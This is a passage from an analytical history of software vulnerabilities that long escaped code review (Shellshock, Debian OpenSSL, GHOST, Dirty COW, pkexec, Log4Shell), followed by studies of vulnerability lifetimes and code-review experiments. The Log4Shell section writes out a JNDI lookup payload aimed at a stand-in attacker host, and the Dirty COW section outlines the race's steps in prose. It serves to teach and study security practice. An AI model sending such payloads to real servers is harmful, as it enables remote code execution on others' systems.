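Paying attention to the right feature was not enough either, as Schaefer's experiment and the sudo discussions show. The clearest example is Ormandy, who saw little to worry about in 2004, when he was considering what a user with an account could do. In 2014 he knew that strangers could send text to the parser, and he found a way around the official patch within hours. However many people read the import code, they will see nothing wrong with it if they all assume that the environment contains only the user's own text.

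Wheeler thinks that documentation could have exposed the flaw much sooner. Bash's manual mentioned that users could export functions but did not explain how. If it had stated that Bash interprets any variable beginning with `() {`, he argues, somebody would probably have seen the danger. There is some reason to doubt this, because sudo's advisory published almost exactly that rule in 2004 and the flaw stayed in Bash for another ten years. But people who ran web servers had little reason to read about a flaw in sudo. Wheeler also recommends a security review of the documented behaviour, which might well have worked if the reviewer knew what web servers put into environment variables.

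## How other bugs outlasted their readers, 2006 to 2022

Shellshock became dangerous when strangers gained control of data that had once come only from the user. Capable readers missed six other bugs, all in widely used code, for different reasons.

### Binary search: a proof about the wrong kind of number

Binary search finds a value in a sorted list by checking the middle item, discarding the half that can't contain the value, and repeating on the other half. It takes about a dozen lines of code but is hard to get right. Jon Bentley wrote in *Programming Pearls* (1986) that the first version appeared in 1946, but the first that worked for lists of every length didn't appear until 1962. The book includes his own version, which he proved correct and then tested.

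Joshua Bloch, who had attended Bentley's lectures as a PhD student, wrote the binary search in Java's standard library. His version and Bentley's contained the same bug, as Bloch (2006) explained in *Extra, Extra*. The program finds the middle by adding the positions of the first and last remaining items and dividing by two. Java's ordinary whole numbers stop at 2,147,483,647, and a larger sum wraps round to a negative number. Suppose a list has 1.5 billion items and the value being sought is in the upper half. After the first step, the remaining positions run from 750,000,000 to 1,499,999,999. Adding those two numbers exceeds the limit, so Java puts the middle at about minus one billion, and the program stops with an error because no such position exists.

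Bentley's readers had two decades to notice this bug. The Java version lasted about nine years, until it broke someone's program and Sun, the company behind Java, received a report. Testing could hardly have found the bug in 1986, because it appears only in lists of about a billion items or more, a size that Bloch says was "inconceivable" then. A billion Java integers take up four gigabytes, about as much memory as a 32-bit processor can address.

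Bentley's proof assumed that the line sets the middle to the average of the two ends, rounded down. This is true of whole numbers in mathematics, which have no upper limit, but not of those in a computer. A proof that used 32-bit numbers would have failed at this line. Bloch concluded that programmers must test as well as prove, but Bentley had done both. People have since argued about whether the fault lies in the algorithm or in the computer's integers, according to *a survey of binary search*.

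Bloch's article also suggested a one-line correction for C programs, which was wrong too because it added the two positions before converting the sum to a type that can hold larger numbers. The blog post *Binary Searches and Mergesorts Still Broken?* (2006) objected within four days that the correction did not address the underlying problem. Bloch changed the line in February 2008, after Antoine Trux of Nokia pointed out that the C standard does not define the result when such a sum overflows. The corrected line has an extra closing bracket, which a compiler would catch immediately.

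### Debian's OpenSSL: a question on a mailing list

Debian's bug began when somebody changed working code. An encryption key is safe only if nobody can guess the random numbers used to make it. OpenSSL collected unpredictable data, mixed it into an internal pool and generated keys from the pool. It also mixed in the contents of some memory that the program had not yet filled. This did no harm, but it set off warnings in Valgrind, a tool that detects the use of unfilled memory.

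In May 2006 Kurt Roeckx, who maintained the OpenSSL package for the Linux distribution Debian, raised the warnings on the OpenSSL developers' mailing list. He had traced them to two lines and proposed removing both, but said he did not know how this would affect the random numbers. A member of the OpenSSL team replied that he favoured removing them if it helped with debugging.

The two lines had identical text, but one mixed in leftover memory and was not needed, while the other mixed in all the data that callers supplied, including the unpredictable data. Without the second line, any attempt to add randomness had no effect, as a reader commented under Slashdot's *Debian Bug Leaves Private SSL/SSH Keys Guessable*. The main thing that still varied was the number Linux gives each running program, which by default had at most 32,768 values. An attacker could generate every possible key of a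 given type and size in advance and try them all.

Debian uploaded the first faulty version on 17 September 2006. Luciano Bello discovered the flaw, which the project announced on 13 May 2008, almost twenty months after the upload. The fix did not repair existing keys, so the advisory, Weimer's *New openssl packages fix predictable random number generator* (2008), told users to replace every key the faulty versions had generated. It also told them to treat any key for DSA, one kind of digital signature, as compromised if they had merely used it on an affected machine, because each DSA signature needs a fresh secret number.

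Roeckx asked the people who knew the code, as a careful outsider should, but both his question and their answer were about debugging. To judge the proposal properly, someone would have had to open the file and work out what each line did in its own function. Afterwards the change existed only in Debian's copy, so people who read OpenSSL's own repository never saw it.

Each key looked random on its own, so somebody would have had to compare many keys to notice the problem. If all 32,768 values had been equally likely, they would have needed about 213 keys of the same type and size, made on the same kind of machine, for an even chance of finding two the same.

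### GHOST: fixed without being recognised

A developer did notice the mistake behind GHOST, and corrected it. Many servers remained vulnerable for another twenty months.

Programs call the GNU C Library, or glibc, to turn a name such as example.org into a numeric address. If the name consists of digits and dots, one function skips the search and copies the name into a buffer along with some other data. This function slightly underestimated the space it needed, so it could write a few bytes past the end of the buffer. According to iSEC Research Labs (2015), the name had to be at least a kilobyte long, contain only digits and at most three dots, and begin and end with a digit. Nobody looks up such a name by accident, but an attacker could use those few bytes to take over a program despite the usual defences.

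The flaw first appeared in glibc 2.2, released on 10 November 2000. In January 2013, Klotz reported a misleading error code he got when looking up a machine on his own network, in *gethostbyname_r() returns EINVAL (22) instead of ERANGE (34)* (2013). His example in Sourceware's bug tracker showed the wrong code with a buffer of 37 bytes and the right one with 38. Nine days later, Schwab, a glibc developer, posted a patch, *Fix parsing of numeric hosts in gethostbyname_r* (2013). Its list of faults began with "the computed size is too small". Schwab (2013) sent a revised patch on 21 May that corrected the calculation and added a test.

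The flaw was a textbook vulnerability: a buffer that was too small, in a C function that handles names from the network. Yet nobody classified the fix as a security matter, according to Qualys (2015), the security firm that later publicised the flaw. Many Linux distributions keep the same version of a library for years and add only selected fixes, mostly for security. Debian 7 and Red Hat Enterprise Linux 6 therefore kept the faulty code, as did Red Hat Enterprise Linux 7, which came out more than a year after the fix.

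Qualys found the flaw independently during a code audit, described in *The GHOST Vulnerability* (2015), and announced it on 27 January 2015. GHOST therefore lasted twelve and a half years, but more than fourteen for users of those distributions.

The bug also endangered fewer programs than the headlines suggested. In a reply on a security mailing list, Qualys (2015) listed 23 widely used programs or packages, including Apache, nginx and OpenSSH, in which its researchers believed nobody could trigger the overflow. They asked others to check in case they had missed something. Less than six weeks after the announcement, Kaigorodov (2015) recorded that Arjun Shankar of Red Hat had found another miscalculated buffer size in the same family of functions.

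Developers often misjudge which memory errors an attacker can use. Three vulnerabilities found in the mail program qmail in 2005 went unfixed because people thought nobody could exploit them in a normal installation. Qualys later exploited one of them remotely, according to Packet Storm, an archive of security advisories. In 2014 Google's researchers met similar scepticism about another glibc bug, which let an attacker write a single zero byte past the end of a buffer. Evans (2014) used it to take over a machine and argued that time spent debating whether a bug is exploitable would be better spent shipping the fix. GHOST supports his argument, but a distributor that ships only some fixes still has to judge which bugs are exploitable.

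### Dirty COW: three days of expert attention

Several of the most experienced Linux developers discussed the lines of code involved in Dirty COW and the type of error that caused it, but still left a vulnerability in the code.

When several programs read the same file, the Linux kernel can keep one copy in memory for all of them. If a program changes its own view of the file, the kernel first makes it a private copy, which is why the technique is called copy-on-write, or COW. Dirty COW was a race condition, a bug that appears only when two things happen in an unlucky order. An attacker could use it to change a file that they were only allowed to read:

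1. The attacker's program asks the kernel to write to its private view of the file, by a route meant for debuggers.
2. The kernel makes a private copy. It then stops treating the request as a write, because it assumes the hard part is over.
3. Before the kernel looks up the page of memory again, another part of the attacker's program tells it to throw the private copy away.
4. The kernel finds the original page instead. It would refuse to write there, but it now thinks the request is a read, so it hands the page over.
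5. The data goes into the original.

The file might be the list of user accounts, in which case the attacker could become the administrator.

In the summer of 2005, Robin Holt found a related race in the same function. Linus Torvalds's fix made the kernel keep treating the request as a write until it found a page marked as modified. In his description of the change, *Fix get_user_pages() race for write access*, he warned that a write could "in theory" reach a page that the kernel had not properly copied, which is also a fair summary of Dirty COW. On 1 August, Torvalds (2005) wrote that the fix "obviously does" work, but that he had not heard whether the person who noticed the problem had tried it.

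The fix did not work on s390, IBM's mainframe computers, which recorded modified pages differently, so the kernel's check always returned "no". A message from Morton (2005) shows that Hugh Dickins had foreseen this. The next day Dickins (2005) confirmed that the new code left s390 broken, and that evening he sent a replacement that he called "quite untested, let alone the racy case" (Dickins, 2005). A day later, Torvalds accepted a tidied version, Piggin's *fix get_user_pages bug* (2005). It handled the failure that Holt had found, in which the kernel gave up on a write before making the copy. But it introduced step 2 above, in which the kernel stops requesting write access once it has made the copy.

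Torvalds (2016) wrote that the race had been "purely theoretical" in 2005 and had become easier to trigger as the kernel's memory code changed. The developers had undone the first fix because of an obstacle on s390, but the race's seeming only theoretical may explain why nobody returned to that fix. Version 3.9 of the kernel removed the obstacle in 2013, and the weaker fix stayed for three more years.

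No one reported finding Dirty COW by reading the code. Phil Oester found it after an attacker broke into a website he managed. He had been recording all incoming web traffic for years and recovered the attack program from the recordings, he told Computing, a trade publication. Computing dates the bug to 2007, but Torvalds's account and the code point to the exchange in 2005.

The October 2016 fix was also incomplete. According to Wilson and Jayawardena's *Dirty COW*, the developers finished it only in 2017. In *the evolution of COW 1*, u1f383 (2025) describes later bugs with the same root cause in the kernel's separate code for huge pages (large blocks of memory) and for shared memory.

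### pkexec: fifteen million arguments, but never none

In 2014 Evans attacked pkexec, a program that lets authorised users run a command as the administrator. Most Linux systems include it by default. It contained a much simpler vulnerability than the one he used.

When a user types `pkexec date`, the program receives a list of two arguments, "pkexec" and "date". By convention the first is the program's own name, so pkexec starts reading at the second. But on Linux a program could start another with an empty list, and pkexec would then read past the end of it. Qualys' *pwnkit* (2022) explains that Linux stores the environment variables directly after the arguments, so pkexec treated the first variable as the command's name. It searched for a program with that name and wrote the program's full path over the variable.

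An attacker could use this to plant an environment variable of their choice. Linux removes dangerous variables before a privileged program starts, but pkexec put one back afterward. Qualys chose a variable that sets where programs look for the code that converts text between character sets. When pkexec next printed an error message, it loaded the attacker's code and ran it as the administrator. The attack worked every time and on every type of processor.

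The flaw was in pkexec from its first commit in May 2009 and became public on 25 January 2022. Several people came near it in between:

- In December 2013, a blogger described how pkexec behaved with an empty list. Schmidt (2022) drew attention to the post the day after Qualys's announcement and commented that its author apparently hadn't realised the consequences.
- In 2014, Evans studied the loop in which pkexec reads its arguments. He found that it wasted a little memory each time a certain option appeared, and exploited this by passing the option more than fifteen million times. His article doesn't consider passing no arguments at all.
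- In June 2021, Kevin Backhouse of GitHub disclosed another serious flaw in polkit, the package that contains pkexec. That one was seven years old, according to Slashdot's *Patch Released for 7-Year-Old Privilege Escalation Bug In Linux Service Polkit*.

According to Ariadne Conill's account, quoted in a kernel patch by Kees Cook (2022), Michael Kerrisk raised the general problem of empty argument lists in 2008, but Linux developers could not agree that it needed fixing. Some other operating systems already refused to start a program without arguments, and Qualys confirmed that pkexec was not exploitable on OpenBSD for this reason. If Linux had adopted the same rule in 2008, the mistake introduced in pkexec the following year would have been harmless.

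The main part of Rybar's repair, *pkexec* (2022), makes the program stop if it receives no arguments. According to a comment in the code, "someone's probably evil-doing" in this case.

### Log4Shell: a feature that worked

Log4j is a library that Java programs use to keep logs, or running records of what they do. It could replace certain expressions with values as it wrote a message, so that `${java:version}` became the version of Java in use. In July 2013 a contributor submitted code for a new kind of expression that used JNDI, a standard Java service that fetches objects by name, sometimes from another machine. The maintainers accepted the code and included it in a test release that September.

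Programs routinely log text from strangers, including the line in which a browser identifies itself, which attackers had used for Shellshock. If a visitor sent `${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/x}` and the server logged it, Log4j contacted the attacker's machine. Java could then run code that the machine sent back. Chen Zhaojun of the Chinese company Alibaba reported the bug to the project on 24 November 2021, and it was public by 9 December.

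Every line of the new code did what its author intended. To see the danger, a reviewer in 2013 had to know that Log4j expanded expressions in log messages as well as in its settings, that those messages often contained text from strangers, and that JNDI could load code from elsewhere. Many people knew one or two of these facts. At the Black Hat security conference in 2016, Alvaro Muñoz and Oleksandr Mirosh showed how an attacker who controls a JNDI name can run code on a server. Somebody could then have searched popular libraries for places where text from strangers reached JNDI, but nobody reported the one in Log4j for another five years.

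The first fix limited what JNDI could fetch, and people found ways around it within days. The next release stopped expanding expressions in messages altogether. Like Weimer's patch for Bash, it kept untrusted text from being interpreted instead of trying to make interpreting it safe.

### Which bugs would more reading have caught?

These six bugs, together with Heartbleed and Shellshock, escaped in roughly five ways. Several belong in more than one row of the table.

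| How the bug escaped | Examples | Would more reading help? |
|---|---|---|
| Not read | Heartbleed after its release; Bash's parser | Yes |
| Read but not noticed | Heartbleed at its review; Debian's change; pkexec in 2014 | Yes, if the new readers miss different things |
| Noticed but not understood | GHOST in 2013; pkexec in 2013; Log4Shell | Only if the reader knows how attackers work |
| Correct under an assumption that stopped holding | Binary search; Shellshock | Very little |
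| Fixed in one place but not another | Dirty COW; GHOST in the distributions | A targeted search would do more |

Adding more readers, as Raymond recommended, works best for code that nobody has read. Heartbleed is the only one of the eight bugs that lasted mainly because nobody had read the code. If one more competent person had read the file containing Debian's change, they would probably have caught the bug.

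Somebody had already noticed both the GHOST bug and the empty argument list problem. Torvalds held that finding a problem is a bigger challenge than understanding it, but in these cases finding it was easier. More readers of the same code would mostly have produced more reports of a wrong error code or an odd program. It would have been more useful for someone with experience of attacks to read the bug reports, or for distributors to ship every fix without first deciding whether it concerned security.

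Log4Shell could arguably go in the row for assumptions, although the assumption that messages were harmless was false from the start rather than becoming false later. Servers were already logging strangers' text in 2013, and anyone who put the available facts together could have seen the problem.

The binary search and Shellshock code stayed the same while lists grew and web servers arrived. Rereading it would help only a reader who knew how people now used it. Writing down assumptions, such as "the list has fewer than a billion items", would have given later programmers something to check, but people seldom write down assumptions they don't know they are making.

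Dirty COW needed a different kind of work, searching for mistakes like one that developers already understood. One person with a good description of the pattern may do better at this than a hundred people without one. In 2005, the developers could also have left a note to restore the stronger fix once s390 allowed it.

### Why these bugs are famous

People remember most of these bugs because they were severe, easy to exploit or present on a huge number of machines, and many also had a catchy name. According to the satirical website dirtycow.ninja, "all the boring normal bugs" matter far more than a spectacular one because there are so many of them. Corbet's *Dirty COW and clean commit messages* (2016) reports that kernel developers have made a similar argument about the many serious bugs that every release fixes. Corbet agreed but thought it a poor excuse for the handling of Dirty COW, whose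 fix went into the kernel among a set of "cleanups" with no mention of the known danger.

The famous cases are therefore good evidence of how readers miss bugs, but not of how often they do. When a reviewer spots a missing bounds check and the programmer adds it before the change goes in, there is no CVE or news story. Bugs that nobody has found, or that only attackers know about, also go unreported. Dirty COW might have remained known only to attackers for longer if Oester had not kept his recordings. Because the six cases were picked for their variety, they also can't show which way of escaping notice is the most common.

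Hindsight also distorts accounts of near misses. Within a day of Qualys's announcement, somebody had found a blog post from 2013, eight years earlier. Nobody looks for the many public posts by programmers about odd behaviours that turned out to be harmless. We don't know how many of those there are, so it is hard to say whether the blogger overlooked something obvious or made a judgement that is nearly always right.

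Suppose that programmers on two projects each make a thousand dangerous mistakes over twenty years, and that reviewers catch 990 of them on one project and 100 on the other. The first project still has ten bugs left, more than enough to fill a history like this one.

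## How long vulnerabilities last: measurements from 2006 to 2026

Version histories, unlike a few famous bugs, can show how long an ordinary vulnerability lasts, at least if somebody has found it. The first researchers to measure this wanted to know whether a program runs out of vulnerabilities as it ages. If it does, old code that nobody changes should gradually become safe.

### Does old code run out of bugs?

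In *Is finding security holes a good idea?*, Eric Rescorla (2005) worried that publishing a vulnerability also informs attackers, who then break into machines whose owners have not installed the fix. Publishing is justified despite this harm if attackers would probably have found the flaw anyway. But if a program contains a huge number of vulnerabilities and researchers find only a small fraction of them, two people will seldom find the same one, and each fix will achieve little.

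If the supply of vulnerabilities were running out, people should find fewer new ones in a given version as it gets older. Rescorla looked for this decline in four operating systems, including Windows NT 4.0 and Red Hat Linux 7.0, and found no clear trend in any. He then grouped 1,391 vulnerabilities by the year in which they entered the code. Of the groups from 1997 to 2000, only the 1999 group showed a clear decline. He could not rule out a constant rate of discovery. Even an analysis that he knew would exaggerate the decline gave a half-life of about two and a half years. He suggested that some vulnerabilities are obvious enough for several people to find, while a large remainder stays almost entirely undiscovered.

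Rescorla's dates were rough because he took them from a public index of the affected versions of each program, and the people who reported flaws often checked only recent versions. In *Milk or Wine*, Andy Ozment and Stuart Schechter (2006) worked from the source code and its history instead. They chose the operating system OpenBSD because its developers had long put security first, so if it showed no decline, less careful projects presumably wouldn't either.

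The study covered seven and a half years of the system's development, starting with version 2.3, released in May 1998. Of the 140 vulnerabilities reported in that time, 87 (62 per cent) were already in version 2.3. At least 61 per cent of the lines in the final version had also stayed unchanged since version 2.3, so the old code was not necessarily worse.

Discovery slowed, from 58 of these old vulnerabilities reported in the first half of the period to 28 in the second. But it took 2.6 years from the release of version 2.3 for people to find half of the 87, and many had been in the code for some time before that release. Ozment and Schechter also tried seven statistical models of how software becomes more reliable. Only one fitted acceptably, and it implied that people had found about two thirds of the old vulnerabilities, which would leave roughly 40 undiscovered.

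The decline might also mean that people were searching less, since nobody had recorded how many were looking or how skilled they were. Shi, Zou and colleagues later extended the OpenBSD data to 2020 and added nine years of Firefox data in *Does OpenBSD and Firefox's Security Improve with Time?* They concluded that both had become less vulnerable with time, although today's developers do not necessarily write safer code. So some code probably does slowly run out of vulnerabilities.

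### Dating a vulnerability

The commit that fixed a vulnerability is usually easy to identify. To find the one that introduced it, researchers often use `git blame`, a command that shows which commit last changed each line of a file. They run it on the lines that the fix removed or altered and treat the commits it lists as candidates.

This method can make an old vulnerability look only a year old if somebody renamed a variable in the faulty line last year. It can also overestimate the age if the fix tidied some older lines nearby. A fix like Heartbleed's, which mainly adds a missing check, leaves few faulty lines to trace, so the researchers have to guess from the neighbouring ones.

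Alexopoulos and colleagues tested several versions of the method on 1,171 CVEs whose introducing commits developers or researchers had already identified by hand. Frank Li and Vern Paxson had used the most recent suspect commit to get a lower bound, which underestimated lifetimes by 347 days on average. Another team had picked the commit that the most lines pointed to and reported 96 per cent accuracy after checking a sample by hand, but Alexopoulos and colleagues measured about 40 per cent.

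Their own method averages the dates of the suspect commits, weighted by how often `git blame` points to each. If it points three times to January 2010 and once to January 2014, the estimate is January 2011. The resulting lifetimes were 117 days too long on average, with a standard deviation of 932 days. An estimate for a single vulnerability is therefore unreliable, but many of the errors cancel out in a large group. For the average lifetime of 100 vulnerabilities, the researchers put the margin of error at about six months.

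Even careful dating of a bug by hand can be wrong. In December 2024 Daniel Stenberg, the lead developer of curl, announced a record bug that had apparently been in the program for almost 25 years. The following month he added a correction to the announcement, *A twenty-five years old curl bug* (daniel.haxx.se, 2024), because a closer search had shown that a much later commit introduced the bug.

Public lists of affected versions are often inaccurate. Blessing, Specter and Weitzner (2021), in *You Really Shouldn't Roll Your Own Crypto*, reviewed several hundred entries. Entries that listed only one version almost always gave the current version and omitted earlier affected ones. Entries that listed "version X and before" were usually wrong too. Using the more reliable records, they found that vulnerabilities in cryptographic libraries were exploitable for a median of 4.18 years, from the first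 affected release to the release of the fix.

Przymus, Fejzer and colleagues (2023) defined lifetime differently in *The Secret Life of CVEs*, counting from the first public mention of a vulnerability. Their median of 34 days shows how quickly projects repair known flaws.

### Eleven projects compared

Alexopoulos and colleagues collected 5,914 CVEs from 11 open-source projects written mainly in C or C++. They used the manually determined dates where these existed and estimated the rest. The average lifetime was 4.1 years and the median 3.0, but projects differed widely. The table shows six of the projects.

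| Project | CVEs with a known fix | Mean lifetime (years) | Median lifetime (years) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Chromium | 1,580 | 2.1 | 1.6 |
| Firefox | 1,498 | 3.7 | 3.0 |
| Linux kernel | 1,473 | 4.7 | 3.7 |
| OpenSSL | 144 | 7.1 | 6.9 |
| PHP | 281 | 7.9 | 7.3 |
| tcpdump | 115 | 8.7 | 8.9 |

By this measure Heartbleed was short-lived. It lasted about a third as long as the average OpenSSL vulnerability.

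Vulnerability lifetimes closely followed the age of the code, and a five-year-old project can't contain a ten-year-old vulnerability, so the table doesn't show how well each project looks for flaws. It would be fairer to compare the age of a project's vulnerabilities with the age of its code. The researchers did this for four projects and found that in each one the average vulnerability was younger than the average line of code. They took this as a sign that searching for vulnerabilities does some good.

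The average age of vulnerabilities fixed in a given year also rose, by about 43 days a year across all the projects. In 2010, a kernel developer had suggested to Corbet that old vulnerabilities were turning up because developers were fixing holes faster than they were creating them, so mostly old ones were left. Alexopoulos and colleagues doubted this, because it should have changed the shape of the distribution of ages, which stayed much the same while the mean rose. They thought it more likely that developers were adding vulnerabilities at least as fast as they removed them, in code that was itself getting older. They also saw signs that the oldest code in some projects, such as Chromium, might be maturing.

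They also looked for an effect of modern fuzzers, which became common around 2016. They expected fuzzers to find a batch of very old bugs at first and then catch new ones quickly, making lifetimes rise and then fall. Memory errors should have shown this pattern most clearly, because fuzzers are best at finding them. But in the kernel, the lifetimes of memory errors followed the same trend as those of other vulnerabilities up to 2020.

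One reason may be that fuzzing a large program is never finished. A project using the fuzzer syzkaller reported a batch of bugs in the kernel's USB code in 2017 and another in 2019, when its developer resumed work. Two of the five longest-lived vulnerabilities with manually assigned dates were USB bugs that syzkaller had found after about 13 years. Developers had fixed more than 3,000 kernel bugs found by syzkaller, but the study did not count most of them because they never received a CVE, so the result does not show that fuzzers are useless.

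### What a constant chance of discovery would mean

The lifetimes in the study roughly follow an exponential distribution. This is the pattern we would see if every undiscovered vulnerability had the same chance of being found each year, however old it was. If the mean lifetime is *m* years, the share of vulnerabilities that last longer than *t* years is

e^(−*t*/*m*).

If the mean lifetime is 4 years, the formula predicts that half of vulnerabilities last less than 2.8 years and 8 per cent last more than ten. If the mean is 7 years, as in OpenSSL, it predicts that half last less than 4.9 years and 24 per cent last more than ten. The formula fits the combined data very well up to about 11.5 years, but it predicts too many vulnerabilities older than about 16 years. It also fits some projects badly, including OpenSSL, where the actual median was 6.9 years.

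If the chance of discovery were constant, old code would have fewer vulnerabilities left to find. With a mean lifetime of 4 years, people would find about 22 per cent of the remaining vulnerabilities each year. If a program started with 100 and nobody changed it except to fix them, about eight would remain after ten years and probably none after twenty. A long period without discoveries would also be reassuring. If the code had a 50 per cent chance of containing one serious vulnerability, one year without a discovery would lower that chance only to 44 per cent, but ten years would lower it to 8 per cent.

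However, if some bugs are much harder to find than others, as in the earlier example of easy and hard bugs, an old vulnerability is less likely to be found in the next year than a new one. Suppose 80 of the 100 vulnerabilities are easy, with a mean lifetime of 2 years, and 20 are hard, with a mean of 40. After ten years about 16 remain, nearly all of them hard. A new vulnerability in this program has a 32 per cent chance of being found within a year, compared with about 4 per cent for one that has already survived ten years.

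The 84 vulnerabilities found in those ten years have a mean lifetime of 2.1 years. Someone who used that mean and assumed that all the vulnerabilities were equally hard to find would expect fewer than one to be left. The true mean for all 100 is 9.6 years.

Alexopoulos and colleagues concluded that their results were consistent with all the vulnerabilities in a project being equally hard to find and people finding them in random order. That may be true of the vulnerabilities found so far, but the data could look much the same if each project also contained a group of vulnerabilities that were very hard to find and still mostly undiscovered.

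### The vulnerabilities that nobody has counted

All these measurements leave out the vulnerabilities still in the code, which is their main source of bias. Researchers can't correct for these the way doctors in a medical trial allow for patients still alive at the end, because nobody has a list of undiscovered vulnerabilities. The measured average lifetime is therefore too low for the whole population, by an unknown amount.

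The average also tends to rise as people find old vulnerabilities. In the mixed example, a second decade of searching finds only about four more vulnerabilities, but their average age is about 14 years. Recent code, by contrast, looks safe when people have not yet had time to find its flaws.

Stenberg's records for curl show both effects. He traces every confirmed vulnerability to the release that first contained it and, for recent decades, to the exact commit. By July 2025 there were 167, according to *more views on curl vulnerabilities* (daniel.haxx.se, 2025). Their average age when fixed was about eight years and the median about six, and twelve had lasted more than twenty years. A release from the end of 2013 contained 87 of the vulnerabilities now known. Newer releases seem to contain far fewer, but Stenberg expects the figures for at least the last six to ten years to change.

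The auditors who examined curl in 2016 missed at least 42 vulnerabilities in the version they read. These were among the 71 more that people reported over the next six years, according to daniel.haxx.se in 2022. The true number must be higher, since people have kept finding old flaws.

Curl also differs from the projects whose vulnerabilities were younger than the surrounding code. *curl source code age* (daniel.haxx.se, 2024) reports that more than half of the code dated from 2020 or later. Two months later, the median age of curl's vulnerabilities when fixed was a little over seven years. This comparison is rough because even a trivial edit makes a line count as new.

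Stenberg wrote in *keep finding old security problems* (daniel.haxx.se, 2017) that such old flaws keep appearing because better tools find problems that earlier ones missed and because the oldest code gets a year older every year. In *fixed vulnerabilities were once created* (daniel.haxx.se, 2021), the average age of the vulnerabilities was already over 2,700 days, or more than seven years. In March 2026 Stenberg, posting as bagder, announced a new record age of 24.97 years and an average of eight.

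That record was broken in June 2026, when a curl release fixed 18 vulnerabilities, including one that had been in the code since March 2001, according to SecurityWeek's *25-Year-Old Vulnerability Patched in Curl*. The bug was part of a wave of reports from people using AI tools. Stenberg (2026) wrote in *High volume AI vulnerability reports* that "These bugs already existed".

In 2024 Stenberg proposed amending Linus's law to "Given enough eyeballs and time, all bugs are shallow". This is easier to defend than Raymond's version, but it's not much help to people using a program today unless they know how much time is enough.

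### The Linux kernel in 2026

The largest recent measurement covers bugs of all kinds. When kernel developers fix a bug, they often add a "Fixes:" tag that identifies the commit that introduced it. Qu (2026), in *Kernel bugs hide for 2 years on average. Some hide for 20*, collected 125,183 pairs of bug-introducing commits and their fixes, dating from April 2005 to January 2026. The mean bug lifetime was 2.1 years and the median 0.7, and 4.2 per cent of the bugs lasted more than ten years.

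These figures are much lower than the 4.7-year mean for kernel vulnerabilities in the 2022 study, but only 158 of Qu's records have a CVE number. Vulnerabilities might last longer than ordinary bugs, which people are more likely to notice when something stops working. The two studies also used different methods and periods, so it's hard to say how much of the gap reflects a real difference in lifetimes.

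Qu's figures don't fit a single exponential distribution. If they did, with a mean of 2.1 years, half the bugs would last less than about 1.5 years and under 1 per cent would last more than ten. In fact, half lasted less than about eight months, and nearly five times as many as expected lasted more than ten years. A mixture of easy and hard bugs would produce this pattern.

The type of bug may be part of the explanation. Race conditions, like the one behind Dirty COW, lasted 5.1 years on average, while errors in which the kernel tried to use an empty memory address lasted 2.2 years. Alexopoulos and colleagues had found no significant difference between types within a project, although timing-related vulnerabilities also had the longest average lifetime in their kernel data. Qu had many more bugs to compare, but sorted them by keywords in the commit messages and left more than half unclassified.

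One of the oldest bugs was introduced in August 2006, when a developer fixed a fault that could make part of the kernel's networking code freeze. The fix could make the kernel count one user of an object twice and never release the object's memory. The developer who corrected this in August 2025 had to run a particular test repeatedly for about 20 minutes to reproduce the bug.

Bugs fixed in 2025 had lasted 2.8 years on average. Qu attributes the higher figure to a backlog of very old bugs that developers are now finding. The kernel's current history begins in April 2005, so nobody could have measured a ten-year lifetime before 2015. The longest lifetime in the data, 20.7 years, is as long as the history, so that bug may well be older.

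Bugs introduced in 2010 lasted 9.9 years on average, compared with 0.8 years for those introduced in 2022. This difference doesn't by itself show that developers now find bugs much faster because, as Qu points out, no bug from 2022 could have lasted ten years by January 2026. Qu prefers to compare the share found within a year, which rose from 0 per cent for bugs introduced in 2010 to 69 per cent for those introduced in 2022.

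This comparison is doubtful too. Developers surely fixed some of the bugs from 2010 within a year, so the zero probably means few developers were using the tag yet. The 69 per cent is a share of the bugs from 2022 that people have already found, and it will fall as they find more. Detection may well have improved, but these figures can't show by how much.

In *Who Writes the Bugs?* (Qu, 2026), Qu also compared how long bugs lasted depending on who fixed them. Bugs fixed by the person who introduced them lasted 0.88 years on average, and those fixed by someone else lasted 2.59 years. Qu concludes that developers should keep responsibility for their own code. That may be right, but the difference could also arise because people notice many of their mistakes while they are still working on the code, which leaves the bugs they miss for others to find.

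Like the famous cases, the kernel figures leave out the bugs that reviewers catch before a change goes in. Kernel developers review each other's changes by email, and the repository stores only the version that the maintainers accept.

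## Experiments on what code reviewers catch, 2013 to 2026

Experimenters can give many people the same faulty code to review, then count the bugs they catch and the bugs they miss. Basili and Selby did this with ordinary bugs in the 1980s, and several groups have done it with vulnerabilities since 2013.

### Thirty developers and seven vulnerabilities

In a 2013 study, Edmundson and colleagues hired 30 developers to manually review the code of a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities of three types. In one type, SQL injection, a program pastes a user's text into a database command, so a user who types the right characters can change what the command does. The other two let an attacker run code in another visitor's browser or send requests in that visitor's name.

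None of the developers found all seven vulnerabilities, but even a fairly good reviewer will seldom do so. A reviewer with a 60 per cent chance of noticing each one would find all seven only about 3 per cent of the time, and in a group of thirty such reviewers, there is a 43 per cent chance that nobody would.

More experienced developers were not reliably better at finding vulnerabilities. *A security perspective on code review* (Di Biase, Bruntink and Bacchelli, 2016) summarises the result as no relation between experience and effectiveness. Developers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some apparent differences in skill may have been differences in how readily people reported a suspicion. According to *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (Braz and Bacchelli, 2022), Edmundson and colleagues thought manual review could be expensive and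 impractical because finding a vulnerability takes several reviewers.

### A familiar flaw and an unfamiliar one

The hired developers knew they were looking for vulnerabilities, unlike most reviewers of everyday changes. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), Braz, Fregnan and colleagues told their 146 volunteers only that the study was about improving code review. Of these, 105 had at least three years of professional experience. Each reviewed a change of about 140 lines to a Java program that manages employees' holidays.

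For 80 of the volunteers, the change contained a textbook SQL injection. For the other 66, it lacked a check on the number of extra days off an employee wanted to buy, so an employee who entered a negative number would receive money instead of paying. In both versions, volunteers could find the flaw from the code on the screen alone. The researchers also planted an ordinary bug in both versions to see whether people were taking the task seriously, and 52 per cent of the volunteers found it.

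In this first review, 52 of the 80 people (65 per cent) found the SQL injection, and 14 of the 66 (21 per cent) found the missing check. The detection rate was about three times as high for the SQL injection. The paper describes that flaw as seven times more likely to be found, but this figure is a ratio of odds.

The researchers then told everyone that the change contained a vulnerability, without giving its type, and invited those who had missed it to look again. Another 13 people found the SQL injection and 7 more found the missing check, bringing the totals to 81 and 32 per cent. Sixty people, 41 per cent of the volunteers, never found the flaw in their version. Some may not have looked again, because anyone who thought they had already found the vulnerability could skip the second review. Several who missed the negative number said they had mistaken the ordinary bug for the vulnerability.

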